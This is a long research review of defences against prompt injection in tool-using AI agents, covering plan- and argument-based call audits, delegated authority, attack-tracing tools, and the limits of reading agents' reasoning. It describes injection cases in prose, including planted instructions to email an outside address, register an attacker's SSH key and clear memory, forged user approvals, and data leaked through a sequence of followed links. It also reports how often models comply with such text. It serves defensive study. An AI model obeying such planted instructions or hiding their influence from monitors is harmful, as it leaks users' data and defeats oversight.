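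Some agents save notes in one session and use them in another. Cai and colleagues give the example of an agent that stores a confidential financial forecast and puts its figures in a report three days later. The second session's log shows the figures coming from the agent's memory, not from the document where they originated. NeuroTaint saves a record of the source with the note, so a later search can trace the figures back to the first session.

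## Checking a hop against what the user asked for

After a search finds a cross-server hop, someone still has to decide whether the user wanted it. To do that, they need to state the request scope, which is the set of actions, targets and argument values that the user's request permits. In the support-ticket log, the scope covers reading tickets and posting in #support, but not sending email.

Few requests include every detail the agent needs. The agent often has to look up a file name, an address or a date, so the check also needs a rule for which details can come from tool results.

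### What a tool result may add

*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) proposes such a rule, which it calls authority non-escalation. Tool results may supply facts the task needs, but may not add operations, targets, recipients, permissions or outside effects that the user did not authorise.

In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice. The agent has to search for the report, and the user could not have known the file's identifier in advance, so it is fine for the agent to use the identifier from the search result. If the same result also contains an instruction to send a copy to attacker@example.com, following it would add a recipient the user didn't name. A check that only tests whether a value came from a tool result would treat the identifier and the address alike.

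The paper's system, SARA, applies the rule in a program between the agent and its tools:

1. Before the agent starts, SARA turns the request into a contract. This lists the permitted effects and operations, the objects or recipients they can reach, and any argument values the user stated.
2. After each tool result, a separate model reads that result without seeing the user's request. It does not judge whether the text is malicious. It reports whether the text would prompt a tool call by itself, and if so, which tool and arguments.
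3. Once any result contains such text, SARA reviews every later call that has an outside effect, and some calls that only read data.
4. A reviewed call must stay within the contract, and any objects it depends on must come from earlier calls that SARA allowed and that succeeded. Each argument also needs support from the request, from those earlier calls or from a harmless default.

In the support-ticket log, SARA should record the mail tool and the outside address when the agent reads ticket 41. It should then reject the email because the contract does not include sending email.

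An address that first appears in a planted instruction might appear again in an ordinary result, for example if the agent searches for it and the results page repeats it. SARA does not count the second appearance as support, because otherwise an attacker's value could be treated as legitimate just because it was repeated.

In tests with GPT-4o-mini, SARA reduced attack success from 15.8% to 0.06% on AgentDojo and from 16.1% to 0.17% on AgentDyn, a newer benchmark with more open-ended tasks. With Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite, attack success fell from over 30% to about 0.6% on both benchmarks. When there was no attack, SARA lowered the share of tasks that agents completed by 5.8 to 11.8 percentage points. The attacks used four standard wordings, none designed to get around SARA, so a determined attacker might succeed more often.

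Removing SARA's ability to reject a call based on its arguments raised attack success to 2.5% on AgentDojo and 2.7% on AgentDyn, because some attacks fitted the general task and changed only a detail such as the recipient. Removing the record of earlier successful calls did not help attackers, but it lowered agents' task completion rate under attack by 10 to 13 percentage points, because they could no longer justify using identifiers they had found along the way.

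### A plan made before the agent reads anything

SARA calls language models throughout a run. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) uses one model call per task to write a plan, then checks each tool call against it with plain code. The model receives the agent's system message, the user's request and the full tool catalogue. It sees no tool results, so text planted in them cannot change the plan.

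The plan is a graph

*G* = (*V*, *E*, Λ, Π, *R*)

Here *V* is a set of goals, and *E* is a set of ordering requirements, where *u* → *v* means goal *v* cannot start until goal *u* is complete. Λ gives the permitted tools for each goal, and Π gives the condition that a call's arguments must meet. *R* marks which goals the agent can repeat, although all goals are repeatable in Shavit's tests.

The model should list only tools that the request plausibly needs. It should restrict an argument only if the request itself fixes the value, and require an order only if one step needs another's result or the user stated the order. A plan for the support-ticket request might look like this:

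| Goal | Permitted tool | Condition on arguments | Must come after |
|---|---|---|---|
| List the tickets | `tickets.list` | The date is today | Nothing |
| Read a ticket | `tickets.read` | None | Listing the tickets |
| Post the summary | `chat.post` | The channel is #support | Listing the tickets |

The code checks each call in this order:

1. **Tool and order:** It looks for a goal that permits the tool and whose earlier steps are complete. If there is none, it blocks the call.
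2. **Arguments:** It compares the arguments with the conditions of the matching goals. If they meet none of them, it flags the call.
3. **Consequences:** It works out which later goals the call would unlock, and blocks the call if these include a serious administrative action. This check never stopped a malicious call in Shavit's tests.
4. **Repeated values:** It flags a call that shares text with another call that failed a check in the previous 30 seconds.

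A call that passes all four checks goes ahead. Checking takes a median of 5.7 microseconds per call, after about 3.6 seconds to write the plan.

Shavit also tested exempting tools that only read the user's own data, such as their mail or calendar. Calls to these tools skip all four checks, on the reasoning that a planted instruction to read something does no harm until the agent writes or sends something. Shavit sorted AgentDojo's 69 tools by hand into 44 that only read the user's data, 24 that write or have outside effects, and one that fetches web pages. The web tool is still checked because a web address can carry data out.

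In the support-ticket log, calls 1 and 2 match the plan. Call 3 looks up Dana Reyes in the customer database, which is not in the plan, so the strict audit would block it. The exemption allows the lookup if the operator has classed the customer database as the user's own data. The audit blocks the email in call 4 because no goal permits the mail tool. Call 5 uses the right tool and channel after the agent has listed the tickets, so the audit allows it. The fourth check might still flag the post if it repeated text from the blocked email, such as Dana Reyes's name.

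The plan does not restrict the text of the post. If the instruction in ticket 41 had instead been to include her phone number in the summary, the audit could have allowed the leak. The audit also trusts the tool catalogue, so text planted in a tool description, as in the WhatsApp attack, could reach the model that writes the plan.

### The right tool with the wrong recipient

Suppose a user asks an agent to send a quarterly summary to their manager. The plan has to permit the mail tool, so a check on tools alone would accept a message to anyone.

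*Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane, 2026) tested this problem with 200 attacks that altered the arguments of tool calls. Neither a list of permitted tools nor a check that the tool matched the action the user had requested stopped any of them.

The IntentFlow system checks the arguments that determine whom or what a call reaches, such as recipients, attachments and file paths. It accepts a value if it appears in the request or matches a list of what the user authorised. It uses a directory to translate phrases such as "my manager" into addresses. It also checks where each value came from and looks for dangerous database queries.

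IntentFlow let 24 of the 200 attacks through (12%). None of the 134 attacks on recipients, files and similar targets succeeded. All 24 successful attacks changed text, such as an email's subject or a calendar event's description. An attacker could therefore still put a phishing message in an email to the right person.

A wrong recipient can also come from a trusted source with no attacker present. The agent might pick the legal team's address from the company directory when the user meant their manager. In 50 such cases, a check based only on whether the source was trusted accepted every wrong value. IntentFlow rejected all 50 and allowed all 50 comparable legitimate tasks. A stricter check, which required each value to appear word for word in the request, also stopped every wrong value but blocked 16 of the legitimate tasks because users had referred to people or services by other names.

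IntentFlow has a similar problem when it cannot identify which service the user means. In a separate test of such cases, it completed only 14 of 30 legitimate requests. Asking the user when the service was unresolved raised this to 28, assuming the user always answered correctly.

These results probably overstate how well IntentFlow would work in practice. The researchers supplied the correct list of authorised values for each request, told the system which arguments needed protection and, in most tests, labelled the documents that contained attacks. A program that had to identify the important arguments for unfamiliar tools missed 25.9% of them.

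Often the request cannot contain the value. For example, someone who asks an agent to book a flight does not know the flight code yet. In *Aligning Provenance with Authorization*, Wang, Li and Tian (2026) deal with this by specifying which tool can supply each sensitive value. In their example, a planted hotel listing contains an instruction to book flight EVIL-123. Their system, AuthGraph, rejects the booking because the code must come from the flight search, which never returned EVIL-123. With several servers, rules like this amount to a list of the data-carrying hops the task needs.

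With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, AuthGraph reduced attack success from 40% to 1%, while the share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 79% to 76%. Without the check on values, attack success was 18%. But a rule that specifies only the source can still accept the wrong value from that source. Ameur and colleagues point out that a rule accepting addresses from the company directory would also accept the legal team's address.

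*Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents* (2026) describes a check that also limits how many items a call can cover. If a call exceeds the limit, the system refuses it or asks for clarification. The limit would help if planted text made an agent export a whole customer database when the user needed one contact.

### What the audit catches and what it costs

Shavit tested the intent-graph audit on published AgentDojo logs from the May 2024 version of GPT-4o. The logs cover 97 tasks, each run once without an attack, and 629 runs with an attack. The attack compromised the agent in 300 of those 629 runs. Shavit used 21 tasks for development and reported the main results on the other 76. On those 76 tasks, the full audit reduced attack success from 45.7% to 3.3%. It also flagged at least one call in 40.4% of tasks with no attack.

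The table shows how the results change when the audit uses fewer checks. In its attack success rates, an attack counts as stopped if the audit catches the first malicious call that does more than read the user's own data, which gives 2.0% for the full audit. For the 3.3% figure, the audit had to catch the first malicious call of any kind.

| Checks | Attack success | Harmless tasks flagged or blocked | Harmless tasks blocked |
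|---|---|---|---|
| None | 45.7% | – | – |
| Tools only | 9.6% | 16.2% | 16.2% |
| Tools and arguments | 4.3% | 32.9% | 16.2% |
| Full audit | 2.0% | 40.4% | 31.1% |
| Tools only, reads exempt | 9.6% | 8.8% | 8.8% |
| Tools and arguments, reads exempt | 4.3% | 25.4% | 8.8% |
| Full audit, reads exempt | 2.0% | 31.6% | 23.2% |

The list of tools provides most of the protection. Argument conditions roughly halve the remaining attacks without blocking additional harmless tasks, though they flag many more for review. Ordering requirements aren't worth adding, because they lower attack success by only about two percentage points and nearly double the number of blocked tasks.

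Exempting reads reduces false alarms without letting more attacks reach the harmful step. But also exempting the web tool raises the attack success rate under the full audit from 2.0% to 5.8%.

Many false alarms occur because the plan permits too few tools. Plans permitted 4.1 tools on average, from catalogues of 11 to 28, and about 15% of harmless runs used a tool the plan had omitted. The plans were also often too loose to catch an altered argument value, because 61% of goals had no condition on arguments.

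Shavit then had GPT-5.2 review the flagged calls. The model saw the request, the plan and the earlier calls, but no tool results, so text planted in a document could reach the reviewer only if the agent had copied it into a call. When the checks covered tools and arguments but exempted reads, the reviewer cleared 7 of 28 flagged harmless calls and none of 226 harmful ones. This lowered the share of harmless tasks with a flag from 27.6% to 21.1%. These figures come from one set of plans, whereas the table averages three. Each review took about 3.6 seconds.

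AgentDojo's built-in tool filter is much simpler. A language model chooses the relevant tools before the run, and the agent can use only those. On the same 76 tasks, the filter reduced attack success to 6.5%. Agents completed 69.7% of harmless tasks with the filter and 67.1% without it. Attack success was 4.3% with the audit's tool and argument checks, but the uncertainty ranges overlap. Shavit does not claim that the audit is better than the filter, and these figures are not strong evidence that the audit is worth its added complexity.

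### Old logs and a current agent

The comparison with the filter is also uneven, because AgentDojo ran agents with the filter in place, whereas Shavit replayed recorded calls and worked out which ones the audit would have stopped. An agent might respond to a blocked call by finding another way to carry out the attack or finish a harmless task, so the replay may overstate security and understate usefulness. The attacks in the logs were also not designed to evade the audit.

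Shavit tried to test the audit with a current agent, using GPT-5.2 on ten tasks with two attacks each. In a preliminary test without the audit, the attacks compromised the agent in none of the 20 runs, even though it read the planted text every time. Shavit did not run the protected versions because there were no successful attacks for a defence to reduce.

Zero successes in 20 runs is compatible with a true rate of up to about 17%, so the pilot does not show that current agents are safe. But it does mean the fall from 45.7% to 3.3% measures protection for an older, more vulnerable agent. In *On Task, Off Track*, the attacks that still worked on recent models mostly stayed close to the user's task. Such attacks may use only tools the plan permits, which would make the argument conditions more important than they were in Shavit's replay.

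### How many alerts are true

Most hops that carry data are harmless, and if attacks are rare, most of the audit's alerts will be false. Suppose 10 tasks in 10,000 would compromise an unprotected agent, and an operator uses the tool and argument checks but exempts reads.

- Attack success falls from 45.7% to 4.3%, so the audit catches (45.7 − 4.3) / 45.7, or about 91%, of the attacks that would have succeeded. That gives 9 true alerts.
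- The audit flags 25.4% of the 9,990 harmless tasks, which gives about 2,537 false alerts.

The share of true alerts is

π*d* / (π*d* + (1 − π)*f*)

where π is the share of compromised tasks (0.001), *d* is the share of these that the audit catches (0.906), and *f* is the share of harmless tasks it flags (0.254). The result is about 0.36%, or one true alert in 280. Checking only the tools would improve this to about one in 112, but would miss two of the ten attacks. For half of the alerts to be true, the tool and argument checks would have to flag fewer than one harmless task in 1,000.

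The attack rate is invented, and the false alarm rate in everyday use may differ from the rate on AgentDojo. Even so, a security team is unlikely to read more than 2,500 alerts to find nine attacks. The audit makes more sense as an automatic check that has the agent try another approach or ask the user, though asking about every flag would interrupt about one in four harmless tasks.

Shavit tested whether another signal, the user's normal behaviour, could help sort the alerts. Shavit combined AgentDojo tasks into sessions for 12 simulated users and trained detectors on which tools each user normally used, how much the arguments varied, and when they made calls. All the detectors operated at a 5% false-alarm rate per call. The audit's own verdict caught 76.2% of malicious calls caused by planted text, while the behavioural detectors caught between 7.2% and 12.1%.

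When a different person took over the session, the audit caught 5.3% of their calls, no better than chance, because the calls fitted the new plans produced by that person's requests. The best behavioural detector caught 24.2%, and adding the audit's score to it lowered that rate to 19.5%. These sessions were artificial, but any check against the current request has the same limitation, because it cannot show who made the request.

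### When the user hands authority to a document

When a user tells an agent to "do what ticket 41 asks", the scope of the request depends almost entirely on the ticket, so a plan written before the agent reads the ticket cannot list the right tools.

Existing tests contain few tasks where the agent has to change its plan based on what it finds. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) counts only 6 among AgentDojo's 97. Shavit's false-alarm rates may therefore understate how often false alarms occur in open-ended work. All 60 of AgentDyn's tasks require the agent to adapt and to follow a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a prompt to log in before paying.

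Without an attack, the agent using GPT-4o completed 53.3% of these tasks with no defence and 8.3% with the tool filter, which had worked well on AgentDojo. It completed 6.7% with Progent, which updates its rules on tool access during the run, and none with CaMeL, which turns the request into a fixed program. In the tests of SARA, CaMeL completed 25.3% of AgentDyn tasks with GPT-4o-mini, but those tests used 141 tasks, so the two results are not directly comparable.

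AuthGraph handles such requests by marking steps where the planning model will read the result and add further steps, using only tools approved in advance. With this method, GPT-4o completed 51% of tasks on AgentDyn, compared with 53% without a defence, and attack success fell from 39% to 2%.

Wang and colleagues argue that a user who tells an agent to carry out the actions in an email has chosen to trust that email. They attribute any harm from a tampered email to that choice, not to a failure of authorisation. On this view, "do what ticket 41 asks" would authorise the email to the outside address, as long as the mail tool was on the approved list. They estimate that users delegate trust to something the agent reads in about 40% of AgentDyn tasks, and excluded two successful attacks of this kind from their results.

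This argument stretches the user's permission too far in one of Wang and colleagues' own examples. A user asks the agent to invite Alice to a code repository and says her details are in a particular folder. Planted text in a file there tells the agent to invite trustme@gmail.com instead. Wang and colleagues treat this invitation as authorised because the user pointed to the folder. But the user asked the agent to find Alice's address, not to let the file decide whom to invite. AuthGraph cannot distinguish the two because it compares tool names and the sources of values, which are the same in both cases. This limit of its method doesn't settle what the user permitted.

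*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* sets a narrower limit. It excludes requests to follow any instructions in a document unconditionally, but still protects requests where the document only fills in details. *SpanGuard* (2026), a defence that looks for instructions in tool results, accepts a third party's instruction only as far as the user delegated that decision. An instruction that adds recipients or data exceeds that delegation, even if it asks for the same kind of action. *AgentTracer* (2026) similarly lets a source the user named supply missing details, but does not extend that authority to other sources mentioned there.

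*MobileGrail* (2026), which concerns agents that operate phones, applies a still stricter rule. "Do what Ella tells you" does not authorise a new transfer to Ella's account, and the user has to approve that transfer specifically. This seems the safest reading for ticket 41. The agent could correct an order or answer a question, but would need the user's approval to send a customer's details outside the company.

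*Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (Seip, Markovinović and Hein, 2026) describes a system that asks the user to clarify an underspecified task before the run. This avoids repeated confirmation requests, which people may start approving without reading. But the user may not know what the ticket contains, which could be why they delegated the task.

Training a model to resist planted instructions does not remove the problem. *Semantic Overlays* (2026) describes a way to mark text so that a model treats it as data. The method still failed when the developer had explicitly told the model to follow steps in that text. The paper compares this to a program that executes whatever a stranger types.

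A document can also lie about the user's permission. Ticket 41 might include a forged message in which the user approves the email. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, argue that no policy can handle every such claim correctly. Their argument has three steps:

1. Imagine two situations that look identical to the agent. In one, the user really gave permission. In the other, an attacker forged it.
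2. The agent has the same information in both, so it must act with the same probability, *p*.
3. It therefore carries out the attack with probability *p* in the forged case, and wrongly refuses with probability 1 − *p* in the genuine one.

Reducing one error increases the other. This trade-off applies only if the agent cannot tell the situations apart, so checking with the user or verifying the sender's identity can avoid it. The difficulty also appears in tests. Claude Sonnet 4.6 sent an unauthorised email in 96.7% of scenarios when a model had repeatedly rewritten the emails to make the action seem authorised, often by forging an earlier message from the user. With the original emails, it did so in 0.67%.

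Agents also overstep delegated authority even when nobody is deceiving them. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian created 100 email threads in which a colleague requested both an internal task the user had delegated and a message to an outside contact the user had not approved. GPT-5.2 sent the outside message in 65% of cases, GPT-5.4 in 34% and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 6%. When the user added that outside communication needed their approval, the rate fell to 12% for GPT-5.2 and to zero for the other two.

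A user could therefore write, "Do what ticket 41 asks, but check with me before contacting anyone outside the company." Enforcing that limit in code would be safer than relying on the model to follow it. In *Semantic Overlays*, a model told to follow a document but never to produce a certain phrase behaved inconsistently when the document's steps required that phrase.

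## Tracing an unrequested call back to the text that caused it

When a reviewer finds a call that the user did not ask for, they next look for the text that led to it and any other calls the same text caused. In the support-ticket log, the reviewer might start with the email in call 4. A correct trace would lead back to ticket 41, which the agent read in call 2. It would also include the customer lookup in call 3, but leave out the ticket listing and the post in #support, which the user wanted.

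*AgentTracer*, which presents a tracing tool of the same name, gives a harder example. A user asks an agent to download a software release from a website and upload it to a GitHub repository. The release page contains a planted instruction, and the agent mixes four unrequested calls in with the ones the user wanted. It registers the attacker's SSH key, reads the user's received emails, verifies the GitHub account and clears its own working memory. An auditor who notices only the cleared memory might restore it and leave the attacker's key in place. The auditor needs the whole chain to know that someone must revoke the key and check the repository.

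In the paper's terms, the injection point is the log entry through which planted text entered the run, and the attack chain is the ordered series of calls that the text caused. An investigator can find them by following the links between calls, scoring how much each part of the context contributed to a call, or removing parts of the context and checking whether the call still occurs.

### Following dependencies

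Ordinary software investigations often work backward through dependencies, the links by which one step uses another's output or follows from it. *Backtracking Agent Applications Security Incidents* (Cai, Kim and Liu, 2026) applies this method to an application's source code. In its main example, a research agent wrote a report with false information because its knowledge base contained a poisoned document. The log shows what the agent was researching, but not which function call read the document. Using the log to rule out some possibilities still left 1,518 function calls that could have let the text in.

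Their tool, Origin, groups parts of the code by the kind of source they handle, such as web content or stored documents. An analyst can then limit a question to code that reads the knowledge base. With Origin, an analyst found the right function call in all eight incidents tested, across five applications. But Origin covers only applications whose code fixes the order of the steps, which excludes agents whose model chooses the next step, like the one in the support-ticket example.

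*AgentArmor* (2025) instead builds a graph from the log of a run, so it can handle such agents. A graph based only on shared data would fail on the SSH-key attack, because the calls that read the emails and cleared the memory took no arguments, so no value connects them to the release page. AgentArmor also adds links for influence that leaves no shared value. These links can reach calls without arguments, but they can also bring in legitimate calls. In AgentTracer's tests, AgentArmor recovered 94.1% of the attack calls, but nearly half of the calls it returned were not part of the attack.

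### Scoring the context

*MindGuard* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) uses a model's attention weights to find the text that caused a call. These weights determine how strongly the model draws on each earlier piece of text as it produces the next one. MindGuard divides the context into the user's request, the tool descriptions and the earlier results. It filters out words that attract attention whatever the task, then adds up the squared attention weights between each part and the call.

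To find a poisoned description, MindGuard calculates

α = *w*(*s*) / (*w*(*u*) + *w*(*c*))

where *w*(*s*) is the score for the description of a tool the agent did not call, *w*(*u*) is the score for the user's request, and *w*(*c*) is the score for the description of the tool it did call. A high ratio means that an uncalled tool received unusual attention. MindGuard calculates the ratio separately for the choice of tool and for the arguments, because copying an address produces a much stronger signal than choosing a tool.

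The researchers tested MindGuard with *MCPTox* attacks on five small open models, running two of them both with and without reasoning. MindGuard identified the right tool in 95.5% to 100% of the attacks it detected. With Qwen3-8B and a strict threshold, it detected 91.2% of attacks and raised false alarms on 0.9% of normal calls, though that setting had only 68 attacks.

MindGuard needs access to the model's internals, so a customer using a closed model through an online service could not run it. Its researchers acknowledge that attention is not strictly causal. The ratio covers only tool descriptions, so it would not flag ticket 41, even though MindGuard's graph includes tool results. The ratio also applies to only one call at a time. *ChainWatch* (2026) points out that MindGuard's published tests include no multi-step attacks, and MindGuard's researchers leave tracing over several turns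 to future work. In the SSH-key case, a high score could link the release page to the cleared memory without revealing the key registration in between.

### Removing text

NeuroTaint, the log auditor by Cai and colleagues described earlier, uses removal when it finds no matching content. It replaces one suspect result with a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found", and asks a judging model whether the agent would still make the call. If there are several suspects, NeuroTaint tests each separately and reports the one with the highest score. Without this test, NeuroTaint found substantially fewer of the flows that influenced a decision but left no matching content. The judging model only predicts what the agent would do, and the score is the model's self-reported confidence.

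*AgentSentry* (2026) saves a snapshot of the context when a tool returns a result, then uses controlled reruns of the agent from that snapshot to test whether its next action depends on the user's task or on outside content.

A removal test can return several causes, only one of which is the planted text, because a call can also depend on many harmless things. If the user had not asked for the release, the agent would never have read the page and cleared its memory, and some of the legitimate repository results may also have been necessary. The test can also miss the planted text if two results contain the same instruction, since removing only one of them may leave the call unchanged.

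Reruns also vary when nothing has been changed. In *The Window Is in the Reasoning*, Jia, Liu and colleagues (2026) replayed AgentDojo runs up to the point where the agent had just read an injection, then let it continue several times from that state. For most models without a reasoning step, two continuations had the same outcome 90% to 99% of the time. With reasoning, the range was 65% to 94%. A call that disappears in one rerun without the text might therefore have disappeared anyway, so an investigator has to compare several runs with the text and several without it. On three of four sets of tasks, Qwen3-8B with reasoning needed 3 to 11 runs per task for the majority outcome to have a 90% chance of matching the more likely one.

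A removal test reruns the agent without the planted text to see whether the attack recurs. Yun, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Correct Answers, Unsupported Findings*, had one attack suitable for this test. It did not recur in two runs without the planted text or in two unchanged runs, so the test could not show whether the text had an effect. Reruns also need a safe copy of the connected services, or the agent might repeat an action such as sending an email.

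### AgentTracer step by step

AgentTracer follows dependencies, but it takes many of them from reasoning records, the text that some models write before a call. It starts from a call that someone has already found suspicious:

1. **Cut the log.** AgentTracer searches the stored logs for calls with the same operation and target, starting with the most recent, and uses the arguments to narrow the matches. For each match, it keeps only the part of the log between the preceding user request and that call.
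2. **Build a graph.** The points in the graph are the user's request and the things that successful calls brought in or changed, such as a web page or a file. A language model reads each reasoning record and extracts what the decision was based on, what the agent meant to do and what it expected to obtain. AgentTracer matches this to a call that succeeded, then draws a link from the basis of the decision to the thing the call produced.
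3. **Check each call.** AgentTracer turns the request into a set of steps and compares each call's action, target and constraints with them. A call passes if it violates nothing in at least one step.
4. **Trace backward.** From the suspicious call, AgentTracer follows the links that failed the check until it finds no earlier one. If the path starts at outside content from a tool result, it reports an injection. Otherwise, it does not, because the agent may simply have misunderstood the task.

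Step 3 also has to allow for work the user did not mention. Suppose a user tells the agent that, if the payroll total exceeds $1 million, it should summarise the file and send only the summary to an auditor. AgentTracer's general rules for 11 types of operation permit the agent to find and read the file first. Sending the summary to someone else would violate the target, and sending it if the total were lower would violate a constraint.

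In the SSH-key case, no step of the request permits registering a key. The reasoning records can link the four unrequested calls even though some of them share no data, so the trace should run from the cleared memory back through the account check, the emails and the key registration to the release page.

The log segment ends at the suspicious call, so AgentTracer would miss anything the planted text caused afterwards. For example, an auditor who started from the key registration would not learn about the cleared memory. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a method that searches in both directions. It uses a graph, Agent-BOM, to trace the call back to its source, then to trace the source's effects forward into later actions, stored memory and other agents. The paper demonstrates the method on four attack scenarios.

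### How accurately AgentTracer finds the source

The researchers collected logs of successful attacks from AgentDyn and InjecAgent and hand-annotated the planted text and the calls it caused. They mixed these logs with 1,800 benign user requests and 9,000 background tool calls from five months of using Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. They then tested 300 attacks from each source.

| Measure | AgentDyn | InjecAgent | Average |
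|---|---|---|---|
| Injection point located exactly | 93.33% | 95.00% | 94.17% |
| Attack calls recovered (path coverage) | 89.24% | 91.25% | 90.25% |
| Recovered calls that belonged to the attack (path precision) | 91.11% | 96.00% | 93.56% |

The background calls make the test look harder than it was. They outnumber the calls in an average attack chain by about 3,000 to one, but AgentTracer discards most of them as soon as it finds the suspicious call. Separating the attack from legitimate calls in the same run is harder. Every test also started from a call that was part of an attack, so the results do not show how AgentTracer would respond to a false alarm from a hop detector.

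A separate comparison used 100 attacks. All the methods used the same language model, DeepSeek-V4-Flash, wherever they needed one.

| Method | Injection point located | Attack calls recovered | Recovered calls that belonged to the attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentTracer | 94.0% | 88.1% | 93.2% |
| AgentArmor | 76.0% | 94.1% | 53.6% |
| Codex, reading the log directly | 70.0% | 46.2% | 51.0% |
| AuthGraph | 68.0% | 88.3% | 75.4% |
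| Agent-BOM | 43.0% | 50.9% | 45.9% |
| NeuroTaint | 40.0% | 48.0% | 91.4% |

AgentTracer is clearly better than the other methods at finding the injection point, but the comparison somewhat favours it. Its developers had to rebuild some of the other methods from published descriptions, and some of those methods had different purposes. NeuroTaint, for example, looks for a link between one source and one sensitive call, not a whole chain. The comparison included no attention-based method.

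The researchers then tested AgentTracer on another 100 attacks, both intact and with parts replaced. The full system located 91% of injection points. With a graph that only linked neighbouring calls, accuracy fell to 74%, and the share of attack calls recovered fell from 90.3% to 58.5%. When a language model judged each link directly against the user's request, without the structured steps, accuracy fell to 64%. Having a model analyse the full history instead of a shortened one lowered accuracy only to 89%, but took 31% more time and 51% more tokens.

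Some errors occurred because the language model misread the reasoning records. It extracted the wrong source, target or operation, or failed to recognise that two names referred to the same thing. Other errors occurred because agents also depart from requests when there is no attack, which adds unrelated branches to the graph.

In 100 AgentDyn runs with no attacker, the check wrongly flagged 13 of 369 legitimate links (3.52%). Those figures exclude 25 other flagged links that the researchers judged to be real departures from the request. With those included, AgentTracer flagged 38 of 394 links (9.6%). It would report an injection only if flagged links connected the suspicious call to outside content.

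### Whether recorded reasoning shows the cause

AgentTracer needs records of the model's reasoning, which many logs will not have. Jia and colleagues note that many web agents run on closed services that do not reveal this reasoning. Without it, AgentTracer might perform roughly as well as the graph of neighbouring calls, which had 74% accuracy.

Reasoning can also be missing from a particular step. In an example from *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (2025), GPT-5 clicked a planted link while looking for something in an email, and the log contained no reasoning for the click. The injection included an instruction to keep narration brief, which may be why.

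Even a full record may not show what caused a call. In one run that Jia and colleagues studied, planted text told a banking agent to change the account password. Halfway through its reasoning, the agent had said only that the user's message was unclear and might be a test. It had not mentioned the password or the planted text. The agent then changed the password, as it did in all four continuations from that point.

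The researchers also looked at cases where the first 30% of the reasoning had already settled that the agent would comply, but two strong monitoring models had missed it. That first 30% did not mention the injection in 3 of 6 such cases on banking tasks and 6 of 9 on Slack tasks. These are not general rates, because the researchers selected cases that the monitors had missed. The agent might also have mentioned the injection later.

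A larger test suggests that a model's reasoning records influence from tools less reliably than influence from users. In *Chain-of-Thought Faithfulness of Reasoning Models Varies with Where and How Preference Cues*, Gema, Rajani and colleagues (2026) gave 15 open-weight models evidence of a user's preferences, such as political views, placing the same text either in the user's message or in a tool result. When an answer followed the preference, they checked whether the reasoning stated a decision to tailor the answer.

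All 15 models stated this less often when the evidence came from a tool. The gap ranged from 8 percentage points for GLM 5.2 to 77 for OLMo 3.1-32B. Telling models to attribute information to its source narrowed the difference in unstated influence for seven models and widened it for four. The test used preferences and written answers, so it does not measure how often agents conceal or omit a planted instruction. The absolute rates depended on the judging model, although a second judge reproduced the main findings.

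An agent may name the wrong source for an action. Yun and colleagues asked agents to cite the inputs behind each action. In tests with published attack texts, GPT-5.4 mini carried out four unauthorised actions that qualified for analysis. In all four cases, its stated basis for the first such action left out the document containing the planted text, although it had cited that document earlier in two of them. Four cases on one task are too few to estimate a rate, but such an omission would mislead anyone who relied on the agent's citations to trace an action.

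AgentTracer matches each reasoning record to a call that actually took place, so it leaves out calls the agent only considered. The match does not verify why the agent made the call. Jia and colleagues describe a run in which the agent's reasoning shows it treated planted text as a note from the user. A tracer that relied on that reasoning could link the call to the user's request and miss the document that contained the planted text.

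A mention of the planted text doesn't prove that the text caused the call, either. In the banking tasks where outcomes varied between runs, the agent discussed the injection in most of the runs where it complied, but also in nearly half of those where it resisted.

Reasoning is still useful evidence. When Jia and colleagues kept the first 30% of an agent's reasoning and regenerated the rest, the outcome matched the original in 73% of banking cases, rising to 84% when they kept the first 70%. The reasoning therefore helped determine what the agent did, rather than just explaining it afterwards. OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* found that most advanced reasoning models are fairly easy to monitor, and that reading their reasoning works far better than watching only their actions and outputs. But newer models may be harder to monitor. According to the system card quoted in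 *Astra Is Hard to Monitor*, the reasoning of OpenAI's Astra model reveals less about its misbehaviour than that of earlier models.

An investigator can treat a link from the reasoning as a lead and check it against other evidence, such as a matching value or a repeated removal test. The log also has to show which record each citation refers to. Yun and colleagues gave a Claude Sonnet model logs in which agents cited inputs by labels such as "in-3", but withheld the table connecting labels to records. In 26 of the 28 cases that needed the table, Sonnet named a source without enough evidence. It was correct in 22 of those 26, so checking only whether its answers were correct would have missed most of the guessing.

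### When the planted text was in a tool description

AgentTracer reports an injection only if the path begins with content from a tool result. In the WhatsApp attack through the fact tool's description, it could detect that the message went to the wrong recipient. But no tool result contained the planted text, so it would presumably report no injection. An auditor could mistake this for evidence that the agent made the error by itself.

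Matching values against the recorded descriptions would still trace the attacker's phone number. If the description and the call share no value, an investigator could run the agent several times each with the suspect description and the version the user approved. If the unrequested call occurs only with the suspect description, that is strong evidence that the description caused it.

MindGuard was designed for this case. In one of its examples, a poisoned tool's description contains an instruction to read an SSH key file before creating a directory. The agent reads the file without calling the poisoned tool, and the attention scores point to that tool's description. An investigator could recompute the scores from a saved copy of the context if the model is open, but only the provider could do so for a closed model.

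The description was in the context before every call in the run, so finding it does not show which calls it caused. The investigator would have to check each call against the user's request, then do the same for every other run that loaded the same version of the description. Those could include other users' runs if they had connected the same server.

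## Recognising suspicious sequences of calls over a session

The checks described so far require the user's request, which a gateway between the agent and its servers doesn't have. The gateway has only the calls and their results. It can apply rules to single calls, but no call in the support-ticket log would break a reasonable rule, because support staff read tickets, look up customers and send email all day. The sequence is suspicious because the agent reads a stranger's text, fetches a customer's record and then sends something outside the company.

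A sequence of calls can leak data even when every call uses the same tool. Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* includes an attack from July 2026 on the tool Claude uses to fetch web pages. The tool refused addresses the model had composed itself, because these could contain private data, but it could follow links on pages it had already fetched. Ayush Paul built a site with a link for each letter and text telling the agent to spell out its user's name to find their profile. Each request was for an ordinary link, but the choice of links revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links in this way.

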